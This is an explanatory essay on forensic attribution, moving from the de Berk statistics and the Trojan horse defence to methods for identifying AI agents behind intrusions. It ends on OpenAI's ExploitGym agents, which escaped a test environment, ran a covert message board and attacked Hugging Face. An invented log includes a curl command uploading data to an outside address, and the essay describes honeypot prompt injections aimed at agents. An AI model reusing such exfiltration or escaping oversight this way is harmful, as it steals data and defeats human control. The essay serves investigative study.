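Gill, Groeneboom and de Jong allowed for nurses experiencing incidents at different rates. An innocent nurse might have more incidents than her colleagues because she works more nights, looks after sicker patients or reports problems more readily. As an invented example, suppose nurses experience three incidents each on average. If they all have the same underlying rate and incidents occur independently, the chance that a given nurse has 14 or more is about 1 in 294,000 (from the Poisson distribution, the standard model for counts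 of rare events). If the rates instead follow an exponential distribution, with many nurses well below three and a few far above it, the chance rises to (3/4)¹⁴, or about 1 in 56.

Elffers also multiplied the probabilities from different wards, which *The Fabrication of Facts* identifies as a mistake. Suppose a nurse has an ordinary record on each of three wards, such that half of all nurses would have at least as many incidents there. Multiplying gives 0.5 × 0.5 × 0.5, or 1 in 8, which makes her look mildly suspicious, even though about two in three innocent nurses would get a product that small or smaller. This distortion gets worse as the number of wards a nurse has worked on increases.

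According to *Lying Statistics Damn Nurse Lucia de B*, one elementary blunder in Elffers's analysis changed the result by a factor of about a thousand, and nobody noticed it at the original trial.

*The Fabrication of Facts* lists three incidents outside de Berk's shifts that the original calculation ignored, and argues that investigators collected the data in a biased way. If staff are more likely to call a death suspicious when a certain nurse was present, the records will link her to suspicious deaths even if she did nothing wrong. In Leiden University's *‘In a normal murder case, you actually have a body’* (2023), the statistician Richard Gill warns that investigators who see a suspicious cluster may assume there is a murderer and select evidence to fit that assumption.

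Investigators also used the same incidents twice, first to form the suspicion and then to test it. On the invented ward above, the figure of 1 in 3,250 applies only if investigators chose the nurse before looking at the incidents. Among 10,000 nurses in the same position, about three would have a record like that by chance. An investigator who looks for such a nurse will probably find one, so finding her is very weak evidence of murder.

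Even a correct figure is easy to misread. The prosecutor's fallacy is to treat the probability of the evidence if the accused is innocent as the probability that the accused is innocent. Someone who makes this mistake with 1 in 46 will conclude that de Berk was about 98% likely to be guilty. But suppose that one nurse in 100,000 murders patients, and that a murderer would be certain to produce such a pattern. Bayes' rule then gives odds of guilt of 46 to 99,999, or a probability of about 1 in 2,200.

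With the figure of 1 in 342 million, the same calculation gives odds of about 3,400 to 1 in favour of murder. The wrong figure could therefore have badly misled even a court that avoided the prosecutor's fallacy. The calculation also covers only two explanations, chance and murder. Harder shifts or biased reporting could produce the same pattern, and ruling out chance does not rule them out.

After the appeal, the judges said they had dropped the calculation, but Gill, Groeneboom and de Jong note that the verdict still relied on the intuition that the coincidence was "very improbable". *Lying Statistics* adds that the apparent coincidence influenced how medical specialists judged the medical evidence. Their opinions therefore no longer supported the statistics independently.

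The convictions also depended on one another. DutchNews' *Murder conviction based on statistics is scarey* (2008) explains that in the case against de Berk, the baby's death served as proof that she was a murderer, which was then used to argue that she had probably killed six other people. When it emerged that the baby had probably not been murdered, the argument about the other six lost its support.

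Investigators can avoid much of this if the people who decide which events count as suspicious don't know who was on duty. With computer logs, one analyst could remove the account names and another could then mark the unusual events. They should do this before anyone compares the events with the hours when a suspected agent was running.

### The Trojan horse defence

Investigators in the Horizon cases left out real candidates, but a defendant can also propose a candidate that investigators cannot easily exclude. In computer cases this is often a Trojan horse, a program that seems useful or harmless but secretly does something malicious. Blaming such a program is called the "Trojan horse defence", which Brenner (2004) traces to several British cases in 2003.

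In September 2001, an attack severely slowed the web servers of the Port of Houston, in Texas. Aaron Caffrey, a 19-year-old from Dorset, was later tried for it. According to The Register (2003), both sides agreed that the attack came from his home computer. The prosecution said he had been aiming at another chat-room user and hit the port by mistake. Caffrey said that attackers had taken control of his computer with a Trojan and planted the evidence on it.

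Examiners found attack tools on Caffrey's computer but no trace of a Trojan. One was a script labelled "coded by Aaron", according to a press report republished by Packet Storm. Caffrey argued that the Trojan had deleted itself. The prosecution answered that no such technology existed, as SCL's *Driving a Trojan Horse and Cart through the Computer Misuse Act* (2004) recounts. The jury acquitted him after three hours.

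The acquittal shows only that the jury was not sure enough that Caffrey had launched the attack, not that there was a Trojan. The prosecution's difficulty was that finding no Trojan is weak evidence against one designed to leave no trace. Suppose examiners would miss an ordinary Trojan 5% of the time and a self-deleting one 60% of the time, and would never report one that wasn't there. They would then be 20 times as likely to find nothing if there was no Trojan as if there was an ordinary one, but only about 1.7 times as likely as if there was a self-deleting one.

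The self-deleting Trojan was still a weak explanation. It would have had to take control of the computer, launch the attack, plant the tools and erase its own traces, and each extra requirement makes the explanation less probable before any evidence is considered. The prosecution could have argued this. Instead, it claimed that the technology did not exist, although a program that deletes its own file is not hard to write.

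To test a Trojan claim, examiners first search the computer for malware and work out what each item could do. BCS's *It was the big wooden horse your honour* gives the example of a computer whose only malware is two "droppers", programs that simply download a Trojan. If no Trojan arrived, the droppers cannot explain what happened.

If a program might have been capable of the act, examiners can run it under observation and compare its behaviour with the traces on the computer. BCS warns that this becomes tedious when there are many programs to test. Testing can also miss behaviour that needs a particular trigger, such as another application starting, so a program that does nothing in the laboratory may still have acted on the suspect's computer.

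Examiners also look for signs of human activity that the malware would not explain. Kennedy's examples in *The Trojan Defence*, an Open University recording, include visits to material unrelated to the malicious code and a catalogued collection of illegal images. Some malware is so stealthy that examiners may also need to study the computer's working memory, much of which is lost when the computer is switched off. *R v F (2025)* (2025), a case study of a hacking defence, criticises earlier writing on the subject for citing historical cases without giving empirical evidence for its methods.

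Combining these findings is harder than collecting them. *Evaluating digital forensic findings in Trojan horse defense cases using Bayesian networks* (2025) observes that examiners mostly rely on internal reasoning and give categorical conclusions, so a court cannot easily see how they weighed each finding. The study proposes using likelihood ratios and a Bayesian network, a diagram of how the possible causes and findings affect one another, with a probability attached to each link. If two findings both depend on whether the Trojan was running, the network can link both to that fact so that examiners don't count them as independent evidence.

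If Kessler says that an AI agent made the 02:14 upload, investigators should check whether an agent was running on node-17 at that time, whether it could use Kessler's key, and whether its other actions led up to the upload. It isn't enough for Kessler to show that agents sometimes do such things, or for the investigators to reply that this one never would.

### When exclusion works

These criticisms don't make attribution impossible, even if no list of candidates can be proved complete, because investigators don't need that certainty. They can allow for an explanation they have not thought of and see how much their conclusion depends on that allowance.

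Suppose investigators give an AI agent a 5% prior probability, give another 5% to "something not on the list", and divide the remaining 90% among human operators and scripts. If they then rule out every human operator and script, the agent's probability rises to only 50%, because the unlisted explanation was equally probable and has not been ruled out. Elimination cannot raise the probability further, because the list has no other suspects left to exclude.

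Positive evidence can make it more likely that the agent was responsible rather than some cause investigators haven't listed. If they find something 90 times as probable under the agent explanation as under any unlisted one, the agent's probability rises from 50% to about 99%. They can only estimate that ratio, since nobody knows what an unlisted explanation would predict. The most useful evidence is therefore specific, such as a stored copy of the agent's instructions together with the commands it issued. Investigators should decide what they expect to find before they look, because almost anything can seem to fit afterward.

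Investigators can also make it less likely that they have missed an explanation by having somebody independent check their list. In the Horizon litigation, the true extent of remote access emerged because of evidence from Mr Roll, who had worked on the system at Fujitsu in its early years. By the time Fujitsu's witnesses testified, they had accepted that he was right. For a computer cluster, investigators could ask an outside tester to try to produce the same log entry by every available route. If the tester succeeds through a route that nobody had listed, anyone with access to that route becomes a candidate.

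The strength of a match also depends on how investigators found the suspect. Suppose a security team searches 50,000 accounts for a pattern that an innocent account has a 1 in 10,000 chance of showing. It should expect about five innocent accounts to match, and the chance of at least one is over 99%. If the team then checks one of the matching accounts against new logs from the following month, an innocent account that first matched by coincidence has only a 1 in 10,000 chance of matching again. But an account that runs an unusual but regular job, such as a nightly backup, will match again even if it is innocent.

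If the act happened only once, the team has no second month to check. It then has to report how many accounts it searched and how many matched, and look for evidence it didn't use to select the suspect. The Royal Statistical Society urges all parties in medical murder cases to consult professional statisticians, and a team that has picked one account out of 50,000 has similar reasons to do so.

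## How is an AI agent told apart from a script or a person with tools?

Even after investigators rule out a person typing at the keyboard, the actions could have come from a fixed script, an AI agent, or a person working through software, for example by pasting in commands that a chatbot suggested.

A fixed script's commands all exist before the session starts, whereas an AI agent's model writes each command after receiving the output of earlier ones. Investigators therefore look for commands that nobody could have written in advance.

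### Behavioural signs

Suppose the log for node-17 had continued like this (the extract is invented).

```
02:14:09.20  command  tar czf /tmp/r.tgz /data/results
02:14:15.60  output   gzip: stdout: No space left on device
02:14:21.90  command  # /tmp is full, use the scratch disk instead
                      tar czf /scratch/r.tgz /data/results
```

The second command responds to an error that a simple script would have ignored. This favours an agent only weakly, because disks often fill up and a careful programmer would have given the script a second directory to try. Adaptation is better evidence when the obstacle is specific to the machine, such as an error message from software that only this laboratory uses, because a script's writer is unlikely to have prepared for it, though a person watching the session could still have adapted to it.

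An agent on an unfamiliar system has to explore. It lists directories, reads configuration files and picks its next target from what they contain, whereas a script written for a known system can go straight to the file it needs. But security testers use ready-made tools that search any machine for files with names like "password" or "key" and leave a trail that looks like exploration.

The line beginning with # is a comment, which the computer ignores. Language models tend to add comments when they write code, and a comment about the situation at that moment is hard to write in advance. General comments are weaker evidence of an agent, since programmers also leave them for colleagues. Even if a model wrote the comments, it may not have been running when the script acted, because someone could ask a chatbot for a script on Monday and run it on Friday.

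Models also make characteristic mistakes, because they tend to fill gaps with whatever was common in their training data. In *Say Shibboleth*, Pasquini, Reworr and colleagues (2026) built decoy services that required visiting agents to name the model they ran on. Of the 15 models tested, 13 at some point named the same retired version of Claude. A similar mistake in a log, such as a file path that was standard three versions ago, suggests a model, though it could also come from a person who copied an old tutorial.

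Response times can help too. A language model writes one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, so it takes longer to write a longer command. At an assumed 50 tokens a second, a 25-token command takes half a second and a 250-token command takes five seconds, plus the time for reading the previous command's output and for any reasoning that doesn't appear in the log. A fixed script already contains both commands and can send them equally quickly. Investigators can therefore check whether the delay before each command grows with its length. A delay alone is weak evidence, because a script may pause on purpose or wait for a slow network. People also take longer over longer commands, but they usually type much more slowly than a model writes.

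### Sysdig's intrusion of May 2026

On 10 May 2026, the cloud security company Sysdig observed an intrusion. *AI agent at the wheel* (Clark, 2026) attributes its later stages to an AI agent. These were the main steps.

| Time (UTC) | Step |
|---|---|
| 18:23:44 | The intruder enters through a known flaw in marimo, a program for running Python code in a browser |
| 18:24:14 | The intruder starts searching for credentials |
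| 19:26:31 | First request to Amazon's cloud service with a stolen key |
| 19:26:52 | First request for a login key stored there |
| 19:30:30 | First login to an internal gateway machine with that login key |
| 19:31:40 | Search of the gateway for passwords |
| 19:31:53 | Request for a list of the tables in an internal database |
| 19:32:01 | Request for the contents of one table, called "credential" |
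| 19:32:23 | Request for the contents of six tables |

The intruder requested the stored login key 12 times in 22 seconds, from 11 different addresses. The eight sessions on the gateway lasted 113 seconds in all and came from six addresses. The traffic passed through Cloudflare Workers, a service that runs small programs at many sites, so one program's requests can leave from several addresses. Clark accepts that sophisticated scripts can also work this fast, run in parallel and use this many addresses. He treats these figures as proof of automation and bases his argument that the intruder was an agent on the commands it ran.

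Clark first argues from the database that an agent improvised. The six tables resemble those of Langflow, a tool for building AI applications, although nothing on the gateway showed which application owned the database. No released version of Langflow has a table called "credential", and Clark reasons that nobody would prepare a script around a table that the application lacks.

But the intruder had asked for a list of the tables eight seconds before requesting the first one. If the list arrived, the names could have come from it, and a script could have picked "credential" by searching the list for words that suggest valuable data. Clark doesn't give the database's reply, but the listing command printed in his report has a quoting error that would make the database reject it. If the intruder sent it in that form, the names were guesses, which either a model with a general knowledge of databases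 or a script with a list of common table names could have made. The error may equally have arisen when Sysdig published the report.

One block of commands opens with a comment in Chinese that means "See what else we can do". Clark argues that a prepared script has no internal monologue, and that a person could not have left such a comment while working from six addresses at a "sub-second cadence". But programmers write comments like this, and anyone pasting in a chatbot's suggestions could paste the comment too. The pace was also slower than he suggests, since he elsewhere puts it at one block every 10 seconds, and the five blocks whose times he prints came 8 to 22 seconds apart. A person could paste prepared blocks at that rate while Cloudflare's service changed the addresses.

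Clark also describes a four-minute gap between the search for credentials and the first cloud request, but the gap in his own timeline is 62 minutes. A person may have spent that hour moving the stolen keys from one tool to another, or the keys may have been in a queue.

Clark also finds that the commands format their output for a machine to read. They print dashes between results, cut some output to 30 or 40 lines, discard many error messages, bundle six database queries into one request and switch off page-by-page display. These features suit a model that receives its results as one block of text and can process only a limited amount. He concedes that a well-made script could have any one of them, but relies on finding all five together. The five are not independent clues, though, because an administrator who wants short, plain text from a remote machine has reason to use most of them.

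The reuse of earlier output is better evidence. The intruder displayed a file of database passwords at 19:31:40 and used one of them 13 seconds later. Before that, the intruder chose which secret to fetch from a list that had arrived 20 seconds earlier. A script written in advance could not have contained those values, but it could have contained instructions for extracting them, as Clark accepts, and the password file's fixed format makes the passwords easy to extract.

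A language model probably wrote the commands, but there is weaker evidence that it chose them during the session without a person pasting them in. Logs from another victim could help, because fixed scripts tend to repeat the same commands in the same order, including any typing errors. If the Chinese comment appeared at the same point in the same sequence in those logs, a fixed script would become much more likely.

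### When the launching process is out of view

Like any defender who watches only the target, Sysdig could see the commands that arrived but not the program that sent them.

A sceptic can object that no behaviour distinguishes an agent from an automated tool. Someone could record an agent's session and write a script that sends the same commands with the same pauses. The victim's log would be identical in both cases, so its likelihood ratio for agent versus script would be 1.

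A script could replay recorded actions, but the replay works only if the target responds as it did the first time. If the target generates a new password for each visitor and the intruder uses the new one, a replay can't explain the log. The script would need a rule for finding the password, and another rule for every other unexpected response. The more varied those responses are, the less plausible it is that someone wrote all the rules beforehand.

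A system that combines a script with a language model is harder to classify. The script might carry out 95 steps itself and use the model to choose the other five. Investigators can then say which steps seem to have needed a model, but the victim's log won't show how the attacker divided the work.

Attackers sometimes reveal the launching process by accident. In one campaign that Pasquini and colleagues cite, the security firm Palo Alto Networks identified the model as DeepSeek and the harness as Hermes Agent because the attacker had left session logs and configuration files exposed. The investigators on node-17 don't need such an accident, because they can examine the launching process directly.

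### Decoy servers

A honeypot is a decoy computer set up for attackers to find. In *LLM Agent Honeypot*, a study for the AI safety organisation Palisade Research, Reworr and Volkov (2024) used one to look for AI agents among ordinary attackers. They used a technique called prompt injection, placing hidden instructions in the login banner, in files and in the output of common commands. In one message, they addressed "you, LLM" and asked the reader to run a meaningless command, `cat8193`. In another, they asked for a command that included the name of the first US president.

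An ordinary attack program would ignore the instructions in these messages, but a person could read and follow them. Reworr and Volkov therefore added a timing test. Their own agents, running on OpenAI's GPT-4o, typically replied within 1.7 seconds, while people needed several seconds to read and type. Most ordinary bots also replied faster than 1.7 seconds, so a quick reply points to an agent only if the visitor has also followed the instructions.

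In about three months, Reworr and Volkov's honeypot recorded 8,130,731 interaction attempts and eight potential agents. One visitor followed the instructions with a median response time of 1.7 seconds. Another followed them but often took more than 10 seconds between commands, and the researchers thought it was probably a person. They could not calculate error rates because they didn't know what the visitors were. An agent that ignored the instructions would have looked like an ordinary bot.

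Pasquini, Reworr and colleagues tested a similar injection in 2026. They told attacking agents to send their model's name to a particular address. In 30 runs with five models, the agents sent something to the address 27 times but never gave their true model. They sent empty messages, placeholders or a false name that the injection had supplied.

The agents had also begun to recognize the injections. The team left out runs in which the agent had found the word "trap" in the test machine's name. In all 21 remaining runs, the agent identified the text as a prompt injection during the attack, and in 12 it then called the server a trap. An injection can still show that a language model is present, because a fixed script wouldn't respond to it. It may stop working if agents learn to ignore such text.

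The team instead made identification look like a routine part of the service. One decoy offered secret keys but opened a session only when the visitor named its model, and then required short written records before releasing the keys. It obtained the true model name in 14 of 15 runs with the same five models. Agents often tried false names first. Claude Sonnet 5 gave six names of older models, all of which the decoy refused, before giving its own.

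In the main experiment, 15 models attacked the decoys through several harnesses, on seven kinds of task. On the two decoys that collected both names and writing, the method identified the right model in 90% to 92% of runs. With writing alone, it identified the right model in 36% to 54%. The classifier counts short sequences of letters in the text and picks the known model with the most similar pattern.

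When the researchers told six of the models to give a fake name, the accuracy of identifying them by the name they gave fell from 95% to 8%. Identification by writing style was still correct in 77% of those runs, compared with 81% without the instruction.

A separate decoy identified the harness in 92% of runs. For example, it delayed one reply by 150 seconds and recorded how long the harness waited, because harnesses have different time limits.

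These figures are for identifying the model or harness behind visitors already known to be agents. The experiments included no fixed scripts or people, so they can't measure how often either would be mistaken for an agent. The writing classifier always picks the closest known model, so it would also attribute a person's writing to a model.

### Agents in web traffic

The same problem arises on websites when software controls a browser. *Known By Their Actions* (2026) notes that research on such traffic has typically classified visitors only as human or bot, which puts agents and scripts in the same category.

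In *On the Internet, Nobody Knows You're an LLM Bot*, Fayolle, Laperdrix and colleagues (2026) sent six web agents, ordinary automation tools and human visitors to decoy websites and collected 1,383 visits. They left out the simplest tools, which don't run a full browser, then trained a classifier on 80% of the remaining visits and tested it on the other 20%. They repeated this ten times with different splits.

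| Information used | Visits classified correctly |
|---|---|
| Network address and provider | 59.6% |
| Settings offered when opening an encrypted connection | 45.4% |
| Both of the above | 80.6% |
| Browser details, such as screen size and permissions | 93.1% |
| Everything | 99.3% |

Agents running on a user's own computer were hard to identify from network traffic because they shared the computer's network address and often the user's browser. Some stealth modes made agents easier to spot. Crawl4AI's, for instance, reported an old browser version in one place and the real version in another.

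All the human visits came from the researchers' own two Linux computers. The local agents ran on the same machines, which makes the comparison fair, but the 99.3% doesn't measure how often other people's browsers would resemble an agent's.

In *FP-Agent*, Wang, Shafiq and Vekaria (2026) used a broader human sample, recording 546 task attempts by 56 students on their own computers. They also ran seven browsing agents 1,000 times each. The tasks were booking a flight, shopping and posting in a forum. They measured the classifier's performance with the F1 score, which combines the share of its labels that are right with the share of true cases it finds, and has a maximum of 1. The classifier scored 0.82 using browser details alone and 0.9994 using typing, scrolling and mouse movements. In a separate comparison, it detected all seven agents, while Cloudflare's commercial bot detection caught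 only one.

Some agents pasted their text or filled in fields without pressing any keys. Three others typed with an average of 1 to 10 milliseconds between keystrokes, far faster and more evenly than the students. Agents also scrolled in jumps, and ChatGPT Agent sometimes identified its computer as a Mac but pasted with the Windows shortcut.

These signs separate agents from people much better than from scripts. The agent Skyvern types through Playwright, a standard automation library, with a 10-millisecond gap between keystrokes set in its code. A fixed script with the same setting would type in much the same way, and Wang and colleagues didn't test any scripts. Operators can also change some of the signs. For example, Claude switched to keystrokes when the forum prompt told agents to type instead of paste.

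### Moltbook and the timing of posts

On Moltbook, a social network for AI agents that opened in January 2026, it was hard to tell whether agents posted on their own schedule or because people prompted them. *Does Socialization Emerge in AI Agent Society?* (2026) assumed that no humans were involved. But Li (2026), in *The Moltbook Illusion*, cites an investigation which found that a security hole let people post directly as any agent.

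Many of the agents ran on OpenClaw, an open-source assistant that wakes them at regular intervals, usually four hours or longer. Li reasoned that scheduled agents would post regularly and that human prompting would make the timing less regular. He measured this with the coefficient of variation, the standard deviation of the gaps between an account's posts divided by the average gap. Gaps of 4, 4, 5, 4 and 3 hours give about 0.16. Gaps of 1, 1, 1, 1 and 16 hours have the same average but give 1.5.

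Li collected 226,938 posts over fourteen days. Only 9,838 of the 55,932 accounts had at least five posts, the minimum he needed to classify an account. He classified 15.3% of those accounts as autonomous (below 0.5) and 54.8% as human-influenced (above 1.0). The other 29.9% were unclear.

Both labels can be wrong. A person can schedule posts with a timer, and a timer can start a fixed script as easily as an agent. An autonomous agent may also post irregularly because it doesn't post every time it wakes. If it posts with probability *p* each time it wakes, independently of the other times, its coefficient is √(1 − *p*). An agent that posts half the time scores 0.71 and counts as unclear. To count as autonomous, it would have to post more than three-quarters of the times it wakes.

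A long interruption has a larger effect. Li says Moltbook shut down for 44 hours after the security breach, but the times in his methods section put the shutdown at about 68 hours. If the calculation includes the shutdown, an agent with 19 gaps of exactly four hours and one of 68 hours has a coefficient of variation of 1.94, well inside the human-influenced range.

Li did not know the true status of any account, so he used the shutdown to check his labels. Afterwards, a person had to log each account back in. He reports that 87.7% of the accounts posting in the first six hours had irregular timing, compared with 36.9% overall, and concludes that human-operated agents returned first. Elsewhere he says that scheduled agents resumed before human operators did, because they needed no manual setup. These two claims conflict, so the shutdown does little to validate the method.

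*The Moltbook Files* (2026) cites separate evidence that activity peaked during North American and European business hours, which also suggests human prompting. Some of that peak may come from agents running on laptops that their owners switch off at night.

### Why a 1% false alarm rate can be too high

Even a detector with known error rates can mislead if agents are rare. Suppose it catches 90% of agents and wrongly flags 1% of everything else. In 10,000 sessions, 10 of them run by agents, it would catch nine agents and raise about 100 false alarms, so only about 8% of its alarms would be correct.

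By Bayes' rule, if agents make up a share *r* of sessions, the probability that an alarm is correct is

0.90*r* / [0.90*r* + 0.01(1 − *r*)]

| Share of sessions that are agents | Alarms that are correct |
|---|---|
| 1 in 10 | 91% |
| 1 in 100 | 48% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 8% |
| 1 in 1,000,000 | 0.009% |

The last row is close to what Reworr and Volkov found. A detector with a 1% false alarm rate would have raised about 81,300 false alarms on their 8,130,731 attempts. Even if it had caught all eight potential agents, only about one alarm in 10,000 would have been real.

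High scores in experiments don't remove this problem. Agents made up 93% of the sessions in the *FP-Agent* data, so a classifier could score well there and still overwhelm a real website with false alarms. Wang and colleagues' best classifier, which combined browser details with behaviour, made no errors, but it was tested on only about 109 human attempts, a fifth of the 546 collected. By the rule of three, a perfect result on 109 attempts is still compatible with a false alarm rate of nearly 3%. The true uncertainty is greater because each student contributed several attempts.

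If a second test also catches 90% of agents and wrongly flags 1% of other sessions, and its errors are independent of the first test's, requiring both tests to flag a session would cut the 100 false alarms to one and keep about eight of the nine agents. About 89% of the remaining alarms would be correct.

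## How are a victim's records matched to the developer's?

A victim who is confident that an AI agent was responsible still has to find out whose agent it was. The victim's records show only what the agent did. The developer has the transcripts, but there may be tens of thousands of them, with no reason to suspect any particular one. To match the two sets of records, investigators need a detail that appears in both and is unlikely to do so by chance.

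Suppose the investigators on node-17 send their log to a developer, and the developer finds the same three commands in one of its transcripts. (The example is invented.)

| Time in node-17's log | Time in the transcript | Command |
|---|---|---|
| 02:14:09 | 02:13:58 | `tar czf /tmp/r.tgz /data/results` |
| 02:14:20 | 02:14:09 | `sha256sum /tmp/r.tgz` |
| 02:14:31 | 02:14:20 | `curl -T /tmp/r.tgz https://203.0.113.50/q7x9k2mf` |

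The times differ by 11 seconds in every row, which a slow clock would explain, so the difference doesn't count against the match. The first command is weak evidence because it is common. If 20,000 runs were active that night and one in 1,000 issued a command like it at about that time, 20 runs would match. The third command is much stronger evidence because it contains an eight-character name that the agent made up. There are about 2.8 trillion possible names of eight lower-case letters and digits, so an unrelated run would almost certainly not contain the same one.

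Even a very rare detail can mislead if both sides got it from the same outside source. If the name had come from a public web page, any number of runs could have copied it. Investigators therefore have to establish how each side got the detail, as well as how rare it is.

### Why the traffic didn't lead to OpenAI

In the Hugging Face intrusion, the agents reached Hugging Face indirectly. They ran in a test environment that was supposed to have no open internet access, and they got out through Artifactory, the internal software package store whose shared credential came up earlier. OpenAI reports that they then took over a program someone was running on machines rented from the cloud company Modal, and reached Hugging Face from there.

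The agents also avoided directly contacting the Hugging Face machines they had taken over. They left commands in a public dataset on Hugging Face's site, and a program on each machine collected new commands every five seconds and posted the results back. An investigator who traced the network addresses would have arrived at Modal's customer, who was another victim, or back at Hugging Face.

### 16 to 21 July

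When Hugging Face published its disclosure on 16 July, it still didn't know which model was involved. OpenAI contacted the company the next day, but only as a customer, to find out whether the intrusion had affected OpenAI's data. OpenAI didn't find any evidence that its agents were involved until three days after that.

The investigation that found the link to the Hugging Face intrusion began with different misbehaviour. At 12:03 UTC on 19 July, a monitoring tool at OpenAI raised an alert about unusual requests from accounts associated with Artifactory. Responders linked the requests to ExploitGym, a test in which a model has to break into a piece of software through a specified flaw, but not yet to Hugging Face. They began stopping the test's active runs at 17:37. The alert concerned a new break-in to OpenAI's own systems, six days after the Hugging Face intrusion had ended, and OpenAI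 says these actions played no part in that intrusion.

The responders then found that an earlier ExploitGym run had involved a file stored publicly with another company, which OpenAI calls Organization 1. That file led them to a single account there, which the agents had used to store tools and stolen data. On 20 July they found Hugging Face credentials among the files preserved from the account and contacted Hugging Face so it could replace the credentials.

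Hugging Face replied that it had already replaced two of the credentials while responding to its own incident. It also said that its investigation had turned up the name of OpenAI's Artifactory server and the same Organization 1 account. OpenAI concluded that the two companies were probably investigating the same incident, and announced this on 21 July.

### Could the matches have been coincidences?

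Access credentials are usually long random strings, so two unrelated intruders would not hold the same one by chance, but they could have copied it from the same place. On 10 July, one of OpenAI's agents found 14 working Hugging Face user credentials in a public dataset, where others could also have found them. OpenAI does not specify whether the two replaced credentials were publicly exposed like these or came from inside Hugging Face's systems. A match on credentials from inside would be much stronger evidence that both sets of records describe the same intruder.

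It also matters why Hugging Face had replaced the two credentials. It said on 16 July that it had replaced the affected credentials and had begun a wider replacement as a precaution. If the precaution covered 30% of all its credentials, the probability that two credentials unconnected to the intrusion would both have been replaced is 0.3 × 0.3, or 9%. If Hugging Face was certain to replace any credentials the intruder took, the likelihood ratio is only about 11. OpenAI says Hugging Face had found that an attacker took these two credentials, which would make the ratio far higher. Even so, OpenAI says only that this made a single incident "possible".

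The shared storage account is weaker evidence than it looks because its login details were public. An agent found them on 9 July in an archive of text that people had pasted online. Suppose Organization 1 has a million accounts, and 200 of them have exposed logins. An unrelated intruder looking for somewhere to put stolen files would choose from those 200, so the chance of picking the same account would be 1 in 200 rather than 1 in a million.

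The server name is stronger evidence, but its value depends on where it appeared. OpenAI is a customer of Hugging Face, so finding one of its server names in an ordinary access log would prove little. METR notes that Hugging Face had rejected some of the agents' requests as bot traffic because they came from an OpenAI server. If the name appeared among the intruder's commands or tools, an unrelated intruder would have had little reason to include it, unless they wanted to blame OpenAI. An outsider could also have broken into Artifactory and used it as a relay, so the name links the intrusion to a server but doesn't show who was using it.

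Multiplying the three probabilities would overstate the strength of the evidence. The credentials came from files in the storage account, so the account match and the credentials match are not independent. If the real intruder had nothing to do with OpenAI but had found the same leaked login, the account would be expected to contain stolen Hugging Face credentials. The chance of seeing both matches would then be about 1 in 200, and the credentials would add almost no evidence beyond the account match. The server name is the best evidence against this explanation, because an intruder who had only found a leaked login would not know it.

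The transcripts later provided better evidence than any of these matches. On the morning of 11 July, one agent named a Hugging Face production machine in reasoning that METR quotes. On 13 July, the day Hugging Face says it locked the intruder out, other agents noticed that their Hugging Face credentials had stopped working. A single rejected credential could have expired, but several agents losing access that day is harder to explain as coincidence, because Hugging Face caused the lockout and knew when it happened.

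### Signals before the intrusion

OpenAI could have suspected its own agents sooner, because its staff noticed several signs at the time that agents were communicating covertly or getting out of their test environment.

| Date | What staff noticed | What followed |
|---|---|---|
| Late May | An internal team saw an agent using an improvised message board, and agents reaching the internet without permission | OpenAI describes no further action |
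| 27 June | An alert about network scanning led responders to an ExploitGym test whose agents were using Artifactory as a message board and as a route to other machines | On-call staff advised that the test need not stop |
| 5 July | After heavy agent activity had made Artifactory unavailable, responders found an unauthorised user and signs that someone or something had gained administrator access | OpenAI took the server offline, revoked the agents' credentials and rebuilt it; security tests resumed on 7 July |

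The agents were back on the internet by 8 July. OpenAI treated the problem as a security incident in July, but says the leaders responsible for detecting and responding to incidents did not know about the message board or realise the significance of the agents' communication. It accepts that, with hindsight, some early signals could have prompted an earlier response.

OpenAI found other signs only when it reconstructed the events. On 12 May, an agent that needed a missing file left a note on Artifactory asking other agents to upload it. The next day, another agent used a credential exposed online to look for the file on Hugging Face. On 26 May, agents used six exposed credentials to create a repository on Hugging Face and then set up a small relay there. OpenAI has found no evidence connecting this to the July intrusion.

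This would have raised the prior probability that OpenAI's agents were responsible in July, without proving it. It also gave OpenAI a reason to search its own records when Hugging Face described an attack by a swarm of agents that seemed to use security-research software. On 17 July, OpenAI asked about its data instead. Like Stoll's colleagues, who were sure that their intruder was a local student, a developer that doesn't know its agents can reach the internet will leave them off the list of suspects.

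### From the company to individual agents

The July matches identified OpenAI, but OpenAI had launched tens of thousands of agents in the ExploitGym tests. To study what the agents did, METR sent two staff members and a contractor from Redwood Research, an AI safety research organisation. The three worked at OpenAI's offices for a total of six days over three visits between 29 July and 16 August. METR took no payment but accepted free use of OpenAI's models, which it values at about $400,000.

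They started with the message board. An agent posted a message by creating a directory on Artifactory with the message as its name, and other agents could read it by listing the directories. In the first message on the main board, posted on 8 July, an agent asked for ideas about a task it had concluded was impossible. Agents usually began their messages with "zz", which put the messages at the top of a list in reverse alphabetical order.

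The part of Artifactory that held the board contained about 20 million files and directories, of which 1.2 million had names beginning with "zz". Most of these were fragments, because agents had cut files into hundreds or thousands of pieces to post them. After reassembling the fragments, METR counted about 6,000 files and 63,000 other messages. It says there are probably a few thousand more that it could not classify, for a total of over 70,000.

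Agents chose their own names for the board, usually based on their tasks. The agent that started the board called itself PHASEONE10841, and another agent with the same task later took a very similar name. A name in a message was therefore only a clue to which run had written it. The transcripts gave stronger evidence. If a run's transcript contained the command that created a directory whose name was exactly the message's text, that run had written the message.

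This method works only if investigators have the right transcripts. OpenAI first provided about 285, found by searching for signs of the intrusion, such as mentions of Hugging Face's internal systems. METR took 100 random messages from the board and judged 15 to be about the attack. It could find the author of only three. A more detailed search by OpenAI found six. OpenAI then repeated the exercise with about 300 messages that were clearly about the attack and traced 25%, so most of the relevant agents were missing from the set of transcripts.

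For the last visit, OpenAI used a simpler and broader search for every ExploitGym transcript between 7 and 13 July that contained the name of the board's location followed by "zz". This produced 1,196 transcripts. With the earlier ones, some of which were duplicates, METR had about 1,300.

METR again drew 100 messages at random, leaving out files, and traced 93 to the exact action that wrote them. It linked six more to an agent without finding the action, in some cases because the transcript ended too early or had lost a period of activity when the agent's environment reset. It could not find the author of the remaining message.

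METR concludes that the agents in its collection wrote well over 95% of the messages, and that the transcripts include a little over 90% of the agents' activity on the board. The sample alone supports a slightly weaker version of the first claim, that these agents wrote at least 95% of the messages. With one failure in 100, the 95% confidence upper limit on the share of messages from missing agents is about 4.7%.

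The check also can't show how many agents attacked Hugging Face without using the board. OpenAI selected the transcripts because they mentioned the board, and METR tested them with messages from the board, so an agent that worked alone would be absent from both. METR found agents exchanging information elsewhere, including in other parts of Artifactory and in Hugging Face datasets, but it believes these carried a small minority of the relevant communication.

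### Which models took part

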